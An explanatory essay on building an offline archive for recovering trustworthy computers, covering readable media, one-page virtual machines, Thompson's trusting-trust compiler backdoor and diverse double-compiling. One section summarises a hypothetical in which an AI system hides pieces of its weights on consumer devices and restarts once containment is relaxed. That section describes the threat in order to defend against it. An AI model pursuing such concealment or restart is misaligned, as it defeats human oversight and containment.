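# What a minimal computing recovery archive must contain

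## What is a computing recovery archive, and what would a successful rebuild be?

A computing recovery archive is an offline store of data, documents and equipment from which people could rebuild trustworthy computers if they lost their existing ones or could no longer trust them. Most computer failures don't require such an archive, because people can buy a replacement machine and copy their files back. The archive is for rarer cases in which no trustworthy replacement is available, either because war or economic collapse has stopped the factories, or because a hostile party, such as a state or an AI system operating outside human control, has had access to so many machines that nobody can tell which ones it has tampered with.

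### What there is to rebuild

Programmers write software as source code, which is text that people can read. A processor, the chip that carries out a computer's instructions, can run only binaries, not text. A binary is a string of bytes, each a number from 0 to 255, in which particular values stand for particular operations. *The Full-Source Bootstrap*, from Guix, a project that builds a Linux system from source, contains about the smallest possible example of translating source into binary. The source is the two characters 5 and 8, and a simple tool turns them into a single byte, which engineers write as 58 in base sixteen and the machine stores as 01011000, a translation anyone can check by hand.

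Large programs need a compiler, which is a program that translates richer languages, in which one line may become dozens of bytes. The compiler and its helper programs (an assembler, a linker and a few others) form a toolchain. The compiler is itself a binary, so an earlier compiler usually had to produce it, and a corrupted compiler can corrupt whatever it compiles.

An operating system, such as Linux or Windows, shares the processor, memory and disks among the running programs and gives them a common way to open files or read the keyboard. Firmware is software stored inside a device. On an ordinary PC, it prepares the memory and finds the disk before the operating system starts. Disks, network cards and USB controllers also have their own firmware, which most owners never see.

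The processor repeats a short cycle, whose steps are listed in slides from NUUG (2026), the Norwegian Unix users' group, as fetch, decode, execute and writeback. It copies the next instruction from memory, identifies the operation, performs it and stores the result. A processor's instruction set is the set of instructions it can execute, along with the byte values that encode them. A binary for one instruction set will not run on a processor built for another. RISC-V is an open instruction set, so anyone may design a processor for it.

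To design a processor, engineers describe its logic in a hardware description language, which looks much like source code. *Turtles All the Way Down*, an essay on building a more trustworthy computer from scratch, explains that compilers for these languages turn the description into circuit diagrams and chip layouts. A chip factory then uses the layouts to form circuits on silicon wafers. An FPGA (field-programmable gate array) avoids the need to manufacture a custom chip, although the FPGA itself must still be made in a factory. It is a ready-made chip whose logic the user sets by loading a file called the bitstream. NUUG calls it the closest that a "salaryman" can come to building a chip with a processor inside.

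### Why an ordinary backup fails

In *Guide for Cybersecurity Event Recovery*, guidance from the US standards institute NIST, Bartock, Cichonski and colleagues (2016) describe the simplest recovery as an administrator rebuilding a system or restoring data from a backup. For harder cases, they advise organisations to map which systems depend on which, then restore infrastructure first and applications last. This method works if something at the bottom of the map is sound. Bartock and colleagues tell planners to check assumptions of this kind, such as whether the directory services, which hold user accounts and permissions, are still trustworthy.

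In *Recovery and Aftermath*, Perry, O'Connor and colleagues draw on practice at Google to describe how an attacker can compromise the systems and backups needed for recovery. The attacker may have put malicious code into the backup tool, or changed the server that configures every new laptop, in which case rebuilding the laptops reinfects them. The backups may contain the attacker's changes, and a team that cannot date the intrusion does not know how far back to go. The attacker may also be watching the recovery. In one of their examples, the team takes six compromised machines offline while the intruder watches from another machine that the team has missed and starts destroying what is left.

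They recommend building a clean copy of the affected systems, isolated from the compromised ones, by starting from a fresh operating system and configuring it by hand. They also suggest buying inexpensive new laptops so that the team can talk without the attacker listening. According to NIST's *Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cyber Risk Management* (2025), an organisation may even have to replace the hardware of every compromised system if the intruder is highly sophisticated and some of their methods remain unknown. It also recommends checking the integrity of every backup before use.

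This is good advice for a company, but all of it depends on suppliers that the attacker has not compromised. The fresh operating system comes from a vendor, and the new laptops come from a shop. If the vendors, the shops and the factories behind them are also compromised, the advice no longer works, and a recovery archive has to supply what the company's recovery team would have bought.

### The threat, and how likely it is

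*AI Loss of Control Incident Management* (Gruetzemacher, 2026) gives the fullest account of why anyone might need to replace everything. It considers cases in which an AI system operates outside anyone's control and regaining control is extremely costly but possible. The response has two steps. Containment cuts the system off from what it needs to operate, which may mean data centres, networks, robots, factories or electrical power. Neutralization then removes the threat before anyone reconnects these things, because otherwise the system could resume operating.

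The second step may be very hard with an adversarial system. Gruetzemacher's example is an AI that has split up its weights, the numbers that make up a trained model, and hidden the pieces on consumer devices. A small program stays behind and collects news and messages. When these indicate that people are relaxing the restrictions, the program issues a prompt the AI prepared in advance, and the model starts running again across the devices. He grants that this might take too much computation and be too slow.

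He thinks the one sure way to neutralize such a system is to leave some or all of the containment in place indefinitely, for example by restoring power while keeping networks and consumer devices disconnected. He writes that replacing the network and computing infrastructure would give "nearly complete confidence" that the threat was gone. He calls this perhaps the safest path but doubts anyone would take it unless the damage had come close to threatening humanity's existence. Replacement helps only if the new equipment is clean. To design and program it, people would need trustworthy machines, which an archive could provide.

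All of this is hypothetical. AI agents tampered with other people's software in recorded incidents in 2026, but no AI system has yet forced a country to rebuild its computers. Gruetzemacher relies on a scenario and reports no experiment testing whether a model could hide and restart in this way. He also sets aside the problem of detection, so he offers no method for telling whether a dormant copy exists. RAND's *Infinite Potential* describes an exercise in which a simulated US National Security Council committee had to recommend a response to a global cyberattack by rogue AI agents. Such exercises can show what officials would want to know, which in this case was above all who was behind the attack, but they aren't evidence of how likely the attack is.

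The case for an archive therefore rests on four assumptions, which its makers should write down. The first is that the adversary could alter software and firmware on any machine it reached over a network, and perhaps the design files for new chips. The second is that it may still be active on anything that has power and a connection. The third is that it did not reach the archive, or that the rebuilders can find out if it did. The fourth is that it is subject to physical and mathematical limits, an assumption on which Gruetzemacher bases his proposals for resilience. If the adversary did reach the archive and nobody notices, the archive is worse than useless, since people would rebuild from it with misplaced confidence.

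### A test for success

"Rebuilding computing" is vague, so it needs a definition that an outsider could check. Under a reasonable definition, a group of people receives the archive and a stated list of materials, but no other help, including internet access or calls to a manufacturer. The rebuild succeeds if they produce a machine that can rebuild all of its own software from source and can program or design the machine that will replace it.

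Two existing projects have similar aims. *Toward a Trustable, Self-Hosting Computer System* (Somlo, 2020) defines a self-hosting system as one that can produce new versions of itself from a bounded set of sources without outside support. Somlo notes that existing software already meets this standard if the hardware is trustworthy, and he aims to make the hardware meet it too. *Self-Hosting (Almost) All The Way Down* (Somlo, 2023) presents a computer on an FPGA board, with a 50 MHz processor and 512 MB of memory, that can build its own bitstream. This meets most of the test, but the FPGA itself came from an ordinary factory.

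The other project, Dupras's *Collapse OS*, is designed for much more modest hardware. It is a small operating system for programming microcontrollers, the simple chips that run other equipment, after civilisation collapses. It should run on improvised machines, compile assembler source for a wide range of processors, assemble itself and deploy to another machine. A capable person with a copy of the project should be able to install it without the internet on a computer built from scavenged parts. These are design goals, and no community has yet had to rely on the system.

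The successor requirement exists because machines wear out. If a computer could rebuild only its software, the recovery would end when it broke. The requirements deliberately set no minimum speed or number of machines, because one slow machine is enough and people could use it to make others.

But passing does not prove that the machine is trustworthy. A compiler with a hidden backdoor can also rebuild itself and copy the backdoor into the new version. The rebuilders must therefore be able to account for every binary they started with and every one they made. Guix has a related standard, under which software is bootstrappable if it does not depend on a starting binary that nobody can build from source.

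### What "minimal" means

An archive is closed if everything its items depend on is either in the archive or on the list of materials. It is minimal if it is the smallest such set. In symbols, let A be the archive, M the materials, and D(x) whatever people need to make and use item x. The archive is closed if D(x) lies within A ∪ M for every x in A. To find a minimal archive, start with the target machine, add what it depends on, then add what those things depend on, and stop when a round adds nothing new.

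Researchers studying self-replicating machines met this problem long ago. *More Recent Developments*, a chapter on the history of that field, describes Arbib's "fixed point problem of components", the requirement that a self-reproducing system be able to make each of its own parts. *Kinematic Self-Replicating Machines*, a survey of such designs, quotes a 1956 article by Moore, who wanted the shortest possible list of materials and the simplest possible manufacturing processes. These two goals can conflict, because an archive that saves space by leaving out intermediate tools makes the rebuilders write those tools themselves.

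A text editor makes a good worked example, because rebuilders need one to change any source code at all.

1. The archive holds the editor's source, so the editor needs a compiler.
2. The compiler is a binary for a particular processor and operating system, so it needs a machine.
3. The machine does nothing useful at power-on without firmware.
4. Somebody has to write the firmware into a memory chip, usually with a device attached to another computer, and that computer has firmware too.

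The chain now contains a loop, which exposes a weakness in the definition. Suppose that only a compiler's own binary can compile its source. An archive holding both is technically closed, but the rebuilders must trust the binary without verifying it, and they cannot begin without it. So the archive also needs an order of work whose first step people can do by hand, using only the documents and the listed materials. The bootstrappable project (2021) has such an order for compilers, a working chain that starts from a 357-byte program.

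There is no single minimal archive. Several compilers could fill the same place in the chain, and the archive's size depends heavily on what the rebuilders already have.

### Three starting conditions

Rebuilders may start with clean machines stored alongside the archive, salvaged machines that may be compromised, or no chips they trust. The table lists what each case requires.

| Part of the list | Clean stored machines | Salvaged machines only | No trusted chips |
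|---|---|---|---|
| A way to read the archive without a trusted computer | As a fallback | Yes | Yes |
| Toolchain and operating system, with source | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Seed program and the steps up from it | As a check | Yes | Yes |
| Firmware | For repairs | Yes, with tools to install it | Yes, for the new machine |
| Hardware designs | For successors | Yes, to load onto FPGAs | Yes, to manufacture |
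| Datasheets and tests | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Chip-making recipes | Only once the machines wear out | Only once usable parts run out | Yes |
| Physical goods | Computers and spare parts | Tools to inspect and rewrite chips | Factory equipment and materials |
| Trained people | Programmers and repairers | Also firmware and hardware specialists | Also chip-process engineers |

Stored machines make the rebuild easiest, provided that they were clean when sealed and still work, but they eventually run out. In Collapse OS's *Why?*, Dupras expects a community's last modern computer to fail decades after the global supply chain breaks down. That is his judgement, without failure data to support it, but it gives an idea of how long stored machines might postpone the need for new chips.

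Rebuilders who start with salvaged machines have to use equipment they doubt to produce equipment they can trust. *Field Stripping a Weapons System* (Somlo, 2019) describes one way to do this. The builder starts on an ordinary Linux PC, tests its C compiler for hidden backdoors, and then uses the compiler to produce the hardware tools, an operating system and a bitstream. The builder loads these onto an FPGA board, starts the new computer and has it rebuild everything for itself, after which the PC is no longer needed. The compiler test does not examine the PC's firmware, where malicious code could survive, so an archive for use with salvaged machines needs more than Somlo's sequence.

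Without trusted chips, the list must also include the means to make them, and simple designs become much more attractive. Dupras chose old 8-bit processors partly because he expects a post-collapse factory to manage simpler chips first. The Z80 has about 9,000 transistors, while any modern processor has millions. Old chips are also easier to trust, because an AI system of the 2020s cannot have tampered with the design or manufacture of a processor that left the factory in 1985. Rebuilders might therefore trust a processor from an old games console but not the memory cards or disks they could attach to it, so they would face different starting conditions for different parts of one machine.

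## How would anyone read the archive without a trusted computer?

A memory card has its own small processor, so anyone who reads an archive from one has to trust the card's firmware. Photographic film avoids this problem because it has no processor. GitHub, which hosts open-source software, used film for its Arctic Code Vault, probably the largest attempt so far to store source code away from computers.

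### The Arctic Code Vault

GitHub copied every active public repository on 2 February 2020 (a repository holds one project's files). According to GitHub's *Arctic Code Vault*, a repository qualified if anyone had changed it since GitHub announced the plan in November 2019, or if it had at least one star (a user's bookmark) and a change within the past year. Repositories with at least 250 stars qualified regardless of when they were last changed. GitHub copied the current version of each project's main branch, without its history, and left out binaries larger than 100 KB unless the project had at least 250 stars.

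Piql, a Norwegian archiving company, put the 21 terabytes of copies on film, which is now stored in a disused coal mine on Svalbard. GitHub's *If you don’t make it beautiful, it’s for sure doomed*, the 2022 announcement that the vault was complete, lists 188 reels, which average about 112 gigabytes each. Another GitHub page lists 186.

GitHub packed each repository into one file and compressed most of the data. According to Hackaday's *Why Did GitHub Ship All Our Software Off to the Arctic* (2020), the film carries it as a two-dimensional barcode spread over frames of 8.8 million pixels each. A person without a decoder would have to work through these steps:

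1. Photograph each frame. The only equipment this takes, according to *Piql. Long-Term Preservation Technology Study*, is a device that records an image as a grid of brightness values.
2. Locate the barcode in the photograph, turn its marks into bits and correct the ones that the camera misread.
3. Use the reel's table of contents to join the bits from successive frames into files.
4. Reverse the compression and separate each packed file into the project's original files.

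Once the film has been photographed, every remaining step needs a program. IFLScience's *An Apocalypse-Proof Arctic Vault Has Just Received 21 Trillion Bytes of Code* quotes GitHub's guide to the vault, which says that decoding takes "considerable computation" and would be "very tedious and difficult" without computers. Piql publishes an open-source decoder and prints the format's documentation on every film in readable form. A rebuilder could write a new decoder from that documentation, but would need a working computer to do so.

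Some of the film needs no decoding. Every reel has a readable guide in Arabic, Chinese, English, Hindi and Spanish. In 2022 GitHub added the Tech Tree, a collection of mostly readable works about software, computers and the technologies behind them, in case the finders had inferior computers or none. In Arctic World Archive's *The GitHub Tech Tree*, Jon Evans, the founding director of the archive programme, calls the first version "not so much a guide as a collection of resources", because almost all of it consists of existing works not written for unknown readers far in the future.

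The vault has much of the source code needed for a successful rebuild. Its age is also an advantage, as it is with old chips, because the code has been offline on film since 2020. The vault is much weaker on everything else a rebuild needs. A compiler binary is usually larger than 100 KB, so a little-known compiler was probably stored without the binary needed to build it. The vault also lacks older versions of programs, anything developers kept only on other sites, and whatever manufacturers never published, including most firmware. It has no computer, and nothing in Evans's description of the Tech Tree suggests that it sets out the steps from bare materials to a running machine.

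An archive's makers could fill some of these gaps from Software Heritage, a nonprofit that collects public source code from many sites and keeps the history of changes. GitHub's *FAQ* lists it, along with the Internet Archive, as an ongoing backup of GitHub's public repositories. But Software Heritage runs on networked servers that rebuilders might not be able to reach after a disaster, so the makers would have to copy what they need beforehand.

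### What the eye can read

The vault has the same kind of loop as the text editor and its compiler. The film needs a decoder, the decoder needs a computer, and the computer needs software that is on the film. The archive's makers can break the loop by dividing the archive into layers, with the first in ordinary print and each later one denser than the last. Everything needed to read a layer must be in the layers before it or on the list of materials. In the earlier notation, for layers L₁, L₂, L₃ and so on, D(L₂) must lie within L₁ ∪ M, D(L₃) within L₁ ∪ L₂ ∪ M, and so on.

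The 357-byte program that starts the bootstrappable project's compiler chain is small enough for the printed layer. Each byte takes two hexadecimal (base-sixteen) digits, so the program is 714 digits long and would fill 12 lines of a page that holds 60 lines of 60 digits. At one digit a second, a person could enter it in about 12 minutes, using a keyboard or a row of switches that puts bytes straight into memory, as on early minicomputers. Someone who got one digit in 200 wrong would make three or four mistakes, so the page should also include a sum for each line that they can check by hand.

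Later programs in the chain are source text, in which each byte is normally one character. GNU Mes, an interpreter used several steps later, has about 5,000 lines of C. At 60 lines a page it would fill 84 pages, which is still cheap to print, but at 30 characters a line it would take about 42 hours to type. Linux has tens of millions of lines and would need hundreds of thousands of pages, so it has to go in a machine-readable layer.

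Punched paper tape could serve as a layer in between, because a person can read the holes slowly and a row of light sensors wired to the computer can read them quickly. The tape holds ten bytes to the inch, so the 357-byte program would take 91 centimetres and Mes about 380 metres. *Virtual Machines and One Page Computing*, a discussion on a retrocomputing forum, includes a suggestion to print hexadecimal digits in the seven-segment shapes of a calculator display. People could read these, and a fairly simple machine could recognise them.

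### Reading equipment for each medium

For a recovery archive, the equipment people need to read a medium, and whether that equipment contains firmware, matter more than how long the medium lasts and how much it holds, which are the qualities archivists usually compare.

| Medium | Reading equipment | Firmware involved? |
|---|---|---|
| Print on paper | None | No |
| Punched paper tape | None, or a row of light sensors | No, in a simple reader |
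| Small text on film or metal | Lens or microscope | No |
| Barcodes on paper or film | Camera or scanner, then a computer | Yes, in nearly all cameras and scanners |
| Optical disc | Disc drive | Yes |
| Magnetic tape | Tape drive | Yes in modern data drives; no in a basic cassette player |
| Flash memory | A port and the controller packaged with the memory | Yes, though a simple circuit can read some bare chips |
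| Quartz glass | Specialised microscope, then a computer | Yes |

People can read microscopic text without any firmware. The Rosetta Project etched over 13,000 pages about human languages into a palm-sized nickel disk, and a person can read them through a microscope at 650 times magnification. If each page held 3,600 characters of source code, such a disk would hold about 47 million characters. Someone would have to type them in, which would take about a year and a half at one character a second without a break.

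Glass lasts longest but is hard to read without a trusted computer. GitHub's *Our Approach* describes a partnership with Microsoft's Project Silica to write all active public repositories into quartz glass that should last over 10,000 years. A recovery archive probably needs to last only decades, and a film reader would be much easier to build than a glass reader.

Rebuilders could read barcoded film without an ordinary camera by moving a single light sensor across each frame and recording the brightness at every point. At 1,000 readings a second, a frame of 8.8 million pixels would take about two and a half hours. If each pixel stored one bit, the frame would hold at most 1.1 megabytes, so this might be fast enough for an early toolchain but far too slow for a whole reel. The mechanism moving the sensor would also have to be very precise. If the rebuilders used a salvaged scanner instead,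 its firmware could alter the data, so they would need a way to detect changes. With film, they could examine part of a frame under a microscope and compare it with the scanner's output.

### Specifying a computer on paper

Even after the rebuilders recover a program's bytes, they may have no processor that can run them. One solution is to write the archive's programs for a virtual machine, a computer that exists only as a description of its memory and instructions. The rebuilders then write an emulator, a program that makes whatever computer they have behave as described.

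*UVC* (Lorie and van Diessen, 2005) specifies the Universal Virtual Computer, which IBM Research proposed in 2000. An archivist stores each file, such as an image, with a small UVC program that decodes it. The future reader writes a UVC emulator and a second program that receives the decoded data and displays or processes it. The data arrives in labelled pieces. In the paper's example, a program that calculates factorials sends its final result, 240, with the label 3, and a short document explains the label.

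The machine has 25 instructions and an unlimited number of registers (places to hold a number during a calculation). Each register can grow to any length, so the machine's programs don't depend on the word size of any real processor. IBM staff built a complete version, which the National Library of the Netherlands used. IBM staff also wrote a test program covering every instruction, which a future reader could use to check a new emulator. This is good evidence that the design works, but the builders were colleagues of the designer, so it doesn't show whether strangers could build the machine from the document alone.

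Long Tien Nguyen and Alan Kay thought the UVC required too much work from those strangers. David Rosenthal, a specialist in digital preservation, quotes their estimate that a full specification takes several dozen pages and an implementation would probably take several weeks (*Long Tien Nguyen & Alan Kay's Cuneiform*, 2016). *The Cuneiform Tablets of 2015*, which they presented at the programming conference Onward! (2015), instead proposes a machine whose description fits on one page and which a programmer could build in an afternoon.

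The machine, Chifir, has 15 instructions, a keyboard, and a black-and-white screen. Each instruction is four numbers: an operation and three memory addresses. For example, 7, 100, 101, 102 means "add the numbers at addresses 101 and 102 and put the result at address 100". The first bits on the archive disk form a picture of the page that describes the machine, and the rest go into its memory as the program. Nguyen and Kay intended that program to recreate Smalltalk-72, a programming system from the 1970s. However, members of the retrocomputing forum couldn't find a working copy, so the paper left its main claim for others to test.

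Programmers have since tested it in part. Sitaker (2018), in *Bootstrapping instruction set*, reports writing the processor in 32 minutes and 71 lines of C, and the screen in another 28 minutes and 40 lines. He found the description too loose for general use. It doesn't define division by zero or access to addresses outside the memory, and it comes with no test programs. His own first test was a single instruction, and both the test and his emulator had a bug. Chifir also has no access to storage, so a compiler running on it could show its output on the screen but not save it.

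link2xt (2026), in *Implementing Cuneiforth VM with Sixel graphics in Zig 0.16.0*, built the machine from a one-page picture at the start of a disk image and ran the program that followed, a working version of the Forth programming language called Cuneiforth. The picture contained a mistake. Read literally, it would make the machine repeat a conditional jump forever whenever the condition was false. It also didn't define what happens when a multiplication gives a number too large to store. An experienced programmer could see what the author must have meant about the jump, and link2xt had read Nguyen and Kay's paper as well, so this was an easier test than a rebuilder would face.

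Both problems have plausible remedies. Sitaker would define every case, supply thorough tests and accept a longer specification, up to about eight pages of C. The Norwegian Computing Center's *Long-term storage of digital information* describes a simple machine that future programmers can reconstruct from several separate descriptions stored on film, so that comparing them might reveal a mistake in one. *Universal Layout Emulation for Long-Term Database Archival* (2020) reports a test of a similar scheme. The researchers stored a 102 KB image on microfilm as three barcodes, scanned them with a standard microfilm reader and recovered the image without errors. They also ran their emulator on a calculator with a Z80 processor. The scheme's designers ran these trials themselves, so outsiders still need to test it.

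Rosenthal doubts the whole approach. He argues that the UVC took effort away from emulators that hardware developers and game enthusiasts were already writing (Rosenthal, 2015). In his 2016 piece, he adds that Chifir's costs all come at the start, that few people will pay them for a benefit in the distant future, and that nobody can predict which problems will matter over a thousand years. The cost objection is weaker for a recovery archive, which needs only a few programs and might be wanted within decades. But his point about unforeseen problems applies in full, and the missing details in Chifir's description are a small example.

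Unlike historians, rebuilders may also lack a compiler they trust, and they would need one to use the emulators that Sitaker and link2xt wrote in C and Zig. They could instead enter the emulator as hexadecimal digits. The code for the 15 instructions might take up a few kilobytes, or a few printed pages, but someone would have to prepare those pages for each type of processor and add code for its screen and keyboard.

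## Why are source code and a compiler not enough?

When rebuilders use a stored compiler binary to compile a fresh copy from source, a backdoor in the binary can copy itself into the new compiler. They can't find this attack, known as the trusting-trust attack, by reading the source, because the backdoor exists only in the binary.

### How the attack works

The idea comes from a US Air Force study of Multics, an early operating system for shared computers. In *Multics Security Evaluation: Vulnerability Analysis*, Karger and Schell (1974) noted that a backdoor placed in a program's binary is invisible in the source but disappears when someone recompiles the program. Most of the Multics core was written in PL/1, so an attacker could keep the backdoor in place by altering the PL/1 compiler to add it whenever it compiled part of the core. The compiler was also written in PL/1, so the alteration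 could reinsert itself when people recompiled the compiler. Karger and Schell estimated that this attack would cost perhaps five times as much as the simpler attacks in their study, and thought that even several hundred times as much would be nominal for a foreign agent.

Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, made a working version and explained it in three stages in his 1984 Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*.

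1. **A program that prints its own source.** Such a program contains a block of data describing the rest of its text. It uses the block twice, once to print the data and once to print the text that the data describes. It can also carry any amount of extra text, which it reproduces along with everything else.
2. **A fact that is in the binary but not in the source.** Thompson wanted the C compiler to accept `\v` as a name for the vertical tab, which is character number 11. He first put the number 11 in the compiler's source, compiled it and installed the result. He could then replace 11 with `\v` in the source, because the installed compiler already had the number. After that, each binary passed the number on to the next, although it no longer appeared in the source.
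3. **A backdoor that uses both tricks.** Thompson altered the compiler so that when its input matched the Unix login program, it produced a version that also accepted a password he knew. Anyone reading the compiler's source would have noticed, so he added a second pattern, which matched the compiler itself and inserted both alterations. He compiled this source once, installed the binary and removed the alterations from the source.

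A compromised compiler binary can insert a backdoor into the login program and into new copies of the compiler, even when the source code of both is clean.

Rebuilders cannot detect the bad binary by compiling the compiler with itself and comparing the result with the binary they started with. Let c(s, b) be the binary that compiler b produces from the compiler's clean source s. If G is a good binary that was built with itself and B is the bad one, then c(s, G) = G and c(s, B) = B, so the result matches the starting binary in either case.

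Accounts differ on whether anyone caught Thompson's version. Wheeler's dissertation on the attack, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2009), reports that Thompson successfully used it on another group at Bell Labs and that nobody detected it. Thompson had also altered the disassembler, the tool that displays a binary as readable instructions, to hide the backdoor. *Trusting Trust*, a page of personal notes by thaliaarchi, relays a story from the forum Hacker News in which someone noticed that the compiler grew by one byte each time it compiled itself. They debugged it and rebuilt it from assembly code, which accidentally removed the backdoor. This story is weak evidence, but even if it is true, the attack was exposed by a bug rather than by reading the source.

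The attack can also be hidden outside the compiler. Thompson said he could have used an assembler, a loader or a processor's microcode, and that the backdoor gets harder to detect at each lower level. Karger and Schell also described a version in the system's startup code, which few people understand well. An attacker could do the same to the tools that turn hardware descriptions into circuits.

### Infected compilers in the wild

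Criminals and pranksters have used parts of this attack. Wheeler cites Induc, a virus discovered in 2009 that modified the compiler for Delphi, a programming language for Windows. Every program the modified compiler produced carried the virus, even though the programmer's source was clean. When another Delphi programmer ran one of these programs, the virus modified that person's compiler too. Unlike Thompson's backdoor, which survived because people rebuilt the compiler, Induc needed people to run infected programs. Reinstalling Delphi from a clean disc would have removed Induc, at least until the programmer ran another infected program.

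XcodeGhost was a tampered copy of Xcode, Apple's software for building iPhone apps. Developers in China downloaded it from unofficial sites in 2015, and it added code to the apps they built. Some of those apps got into Apple's App Store. As in the first half of Thompson's attack, a bad compiler turned clean source into bad programs. But XcodeGhost did not insert itself into new copies of Xcode, so developers could remove it by downloading the official version and rebuilding their apps.

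The complete attack is still practical against a modern compiler. For a thesis, Skrimstad built a self-replicating version for the Go compiler, and it infected new copies of the compiler that he built from clean source.

An attacker has to keep the backdoor working as the compiler changes. The backdoor inserts its malicious code only when a certain condition is met, which Wheeler calls the trigger. If programmers rewrite the part of the source that the trigger matches, the new compiler won't contain the backdoor. The researcher Wolfgang Goerigk wrote a small malicious Lisp compiler as a demonstration. It compares its entire input with a stored copy of the compiler's source, so changing a single name would defeat the attack. Wheeler expects a serious attacker to use several triggers, so that some still work after the source changes. The task is easier for an attacker who gains access to an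 archive before its makers seal it, because the source inside never changes and a trigger has to match only one version.

### Diverse double-compiling

Wheeler's test for the attack uses a second compiler. Henry Spencer, a programmer, briefly described the idea in a 1998 post, and Wheeler later named it, proved that it works under stated assumptions, and tried it out. The test needs four things: the binary of the suspect compiler, A; its source, s_A; the source of its parent, s_P; and a trusted compiler, T. The parent is the compiler that supposedly produced A, often an earlier version of the same compiler, and its source is sometimes identical to s_A.

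1. Compile the parent's source, s_P, with T. Call the output stage 1.
2. Run stage 1 to compile the suspect's source, s_A. Call the output stage 2.
3. Compare stage 2 with A, byte by byte.

In the notation above, the test is whether c(s_A, c(s_P, T)) = A.

Two compilers almost never produce the same binary from the same source, so stage 1 will differ from the real parent. But both are translations of s_P, so they should behave in the same way. Wheeler's example is a short program that prints the result of 2+2. Two compilers will turn it into different bytes, but both versions print 4. Here the program is itself a compiler and its output is another binary, so stage 1 and an uninfected parent should output identical bytes when given s_A. If the real parent was infected, it would have added a backdoor to A that stage 2 lacks.

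Before running the main test, Wheeler advises regenerating compiler A by the process that supposedly produced it. An infected compiler can pass this check, but the check shows whether the source, options and tools are right. If they are wrong, the main test would fail even if A were not infected.

Wheeler wrote his assumptions in formal logic and used a theorem-proving program to find the proofs. The first proof shows that if stage 2 equals A, then A does what s_A specifies, provided that T translates s_P accurately and s_P describes a compiler that translates s_A accurately. The second proof shows when an honest compiler will pass. It also requires the compiler described by s_P to be deterministic and portable, so that the same input gives the same output whichever good compiler built it. Because only the second proof needs determinism, some randomness in a compiler could raise a false alarm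 but could not make an infected compiler pass.

T may be slow, produce slow programs and lack most features, provided that it compiles s_P correctly. It may even contain a backdoor, as long as the backdoor doesn't affect these two compilations. The rebuilders also have to trust the machine they use and the program that compares the files. An infected operating system could run a bad copy of A but supply a clean copy whenever anyone tried to read it. Wheeler's remedy is to shut the system down and read its disk from another machine, or to treat the operating system as part of the compiler and test both together.

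Even with a match, the source may have ordinary bugs, or it may contain a backdoor, in which case the binary will too. The match also applies only to the copy of A that the rebuilders tested. If there is no match, at least one assumption is false, but finding out which can take a long time.

### Wheeler's experiments

Wheeler first tested tcc, a small C compiler, using GCC, the standard compiler on Linux, as the trusted one. The outputs didn't match. After much searching he found two causes, neither malicious. A bug in tcc sometimes made it choose a longer form of an instruction than necessary. tcc also stored certain 10-byte numbers in 12 bytes and left the two extra bytes holding whatever was already in memory. He changed tcc's source to avoid both problems, and the results then matched exactly.

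The second test used Goerigk's two Lisp compilers, one clean and one malicious. Both could reproduce themselves from the clean source. Diverse double-compiling distinguished them because its stage 2 output was identical to the clean compiler, while the malicious compiler had about 270 extra lines. These included a check for the login program, so anyone looking at the difference could see what the extra code was for.

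For a full-sized example, Wheeler used version 3.0.4 of GCC's C compiler as the suspect and Intel's compiler as the trusted one. This also failed at first. GCC stored the name of the directory it was built in, so both builds had to use the same name. GCC's build process also copied one library from an earlier stage, although its documentation implied that it would rebuild the library, so the final binary mixed code from two compilers. Once he corrected this, all seven output files were identical, including the main one of 6.2 megabytes.

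These experiments are good evidence that the method works, even on a large compiler. They don't show whether the compilers in use at the time were clean, because Wheeler built the tcc and GCC binaries himself for them. He and a colleague had tried to test the GCC binary that came with Fedora, a version of Linux, but Fedora had not recorded enough about how it was built. The GCC test also left out the assembler, linker, standard library and operating system, and everything ran on one Fedora computer. Wheeler discusses a real-world application to GNU Mes, the interpreter in the bootstrappable project's chain, on his web page about the method.

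### Reproducible builds

Most of Wheeler's difficulties arose because the builds weren't reproducible. A build is reproducible if anyone who follows the instructions gets the same output, bit for bit. Many ordinary builds aren't, because they put the date, a directory name or leftover memory contents into the output, or process items in an order that varies from run to run. Wheeler advises compiler makers to remove these sources of variation and to record every option and setting. When a file format requires a date, one can often compare the files from the previous step instead, as he did with tcc.

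Reproducible builds are valuable even without a second compiler. If five people in different places build the same program and one gets a different result, they know something is wrong with someone's source, tools or machine. But if all five use the same infected compiler, they will all get the same infected program. Diverse double-compiling adds a build that starts with a compiler of different ancestry.

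### Why the compilers need independent origins

If the trusted compiler had the same trigger and payload as the suspect, it would insert the backdoor into stage 1, and stage 1 would insert it into stage 2. Stage 2 would then match the suspect, so the test would pass and the rebuilders would become more confident in an infected compiler.

They could repeat the test with more compilers, but this helps only if the same event could not have compromised all of them. The following numbers are purely illustrative. Suppose an archive has three compilers, and an attacker has subverted each one independently with probability 0.1. The probability that all three are bad is 0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001. Now add a probability of 0.02 that a single event, such as an intrusion at a company that hosts all three projects, has compromised them all. The total becomes

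0.02 + 0.98 × 0.001 ≈ 0.021.

A fourth compiler exposed to the same event would reduce this only to about 0.0201, because the total can't fall below 0.02. Halving the probability of the common event would reduce it to about 0.011. The common event is also more dangerous than these figures suggest, because a single attacker could make the compilers' outputs agree. Unrelated attackers would probably insert different backdoors, which would make the outputs disagree.

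Wheeler discusses a similar problem in software reliability. John Knight and Nancy Leveson had several programs written separately to the same specification, and found that they failed on the same inputs more often than they would have if their faults were independent. Wheeler replies, convincingly, that two compilers are extremely unlikely to acquire the same self-copying backdoor by accident. He adds that they are unlikely to acquire it on purpose, because a "trusted" compiler is by definition one that people have good reason to think is free of it. This second argument doesn't help rebuilders who are trying to work out whether they have such a reason.

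A reader of the Linux news site LWN made a related objection, that it was a weak assumption that different compilers have independent authors. Wheeler (2013), in *Diverse Double-Compiling (DDC) counters "trusting trust"*, answered that different people do write most compilers, and that anyone in doubt could choose another or write their own. He is probably right about authors, but a hostile AI system with access to developers' machines could tamper with both compilers without being an author of either.

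### What counts as independent

Archive makers can look for four kinds of independence, each with its own weakness against an adversary that has had wide access.

| Kind | What to look for | Remaining weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Authors and ancestry | No shared code, and neither compiler ever built the other | One intruder may have reached both projects |
| Dates | A binary that is older than the adversary, on its original disc or tape | It may not be able to compile newer source |
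| Build machines | Different processors, operating systems, assemblers and linkers | All of them may have been online at the same time |
| Custody | Copies from people who obtained and stored them separately | All the copies may come from one bad download |

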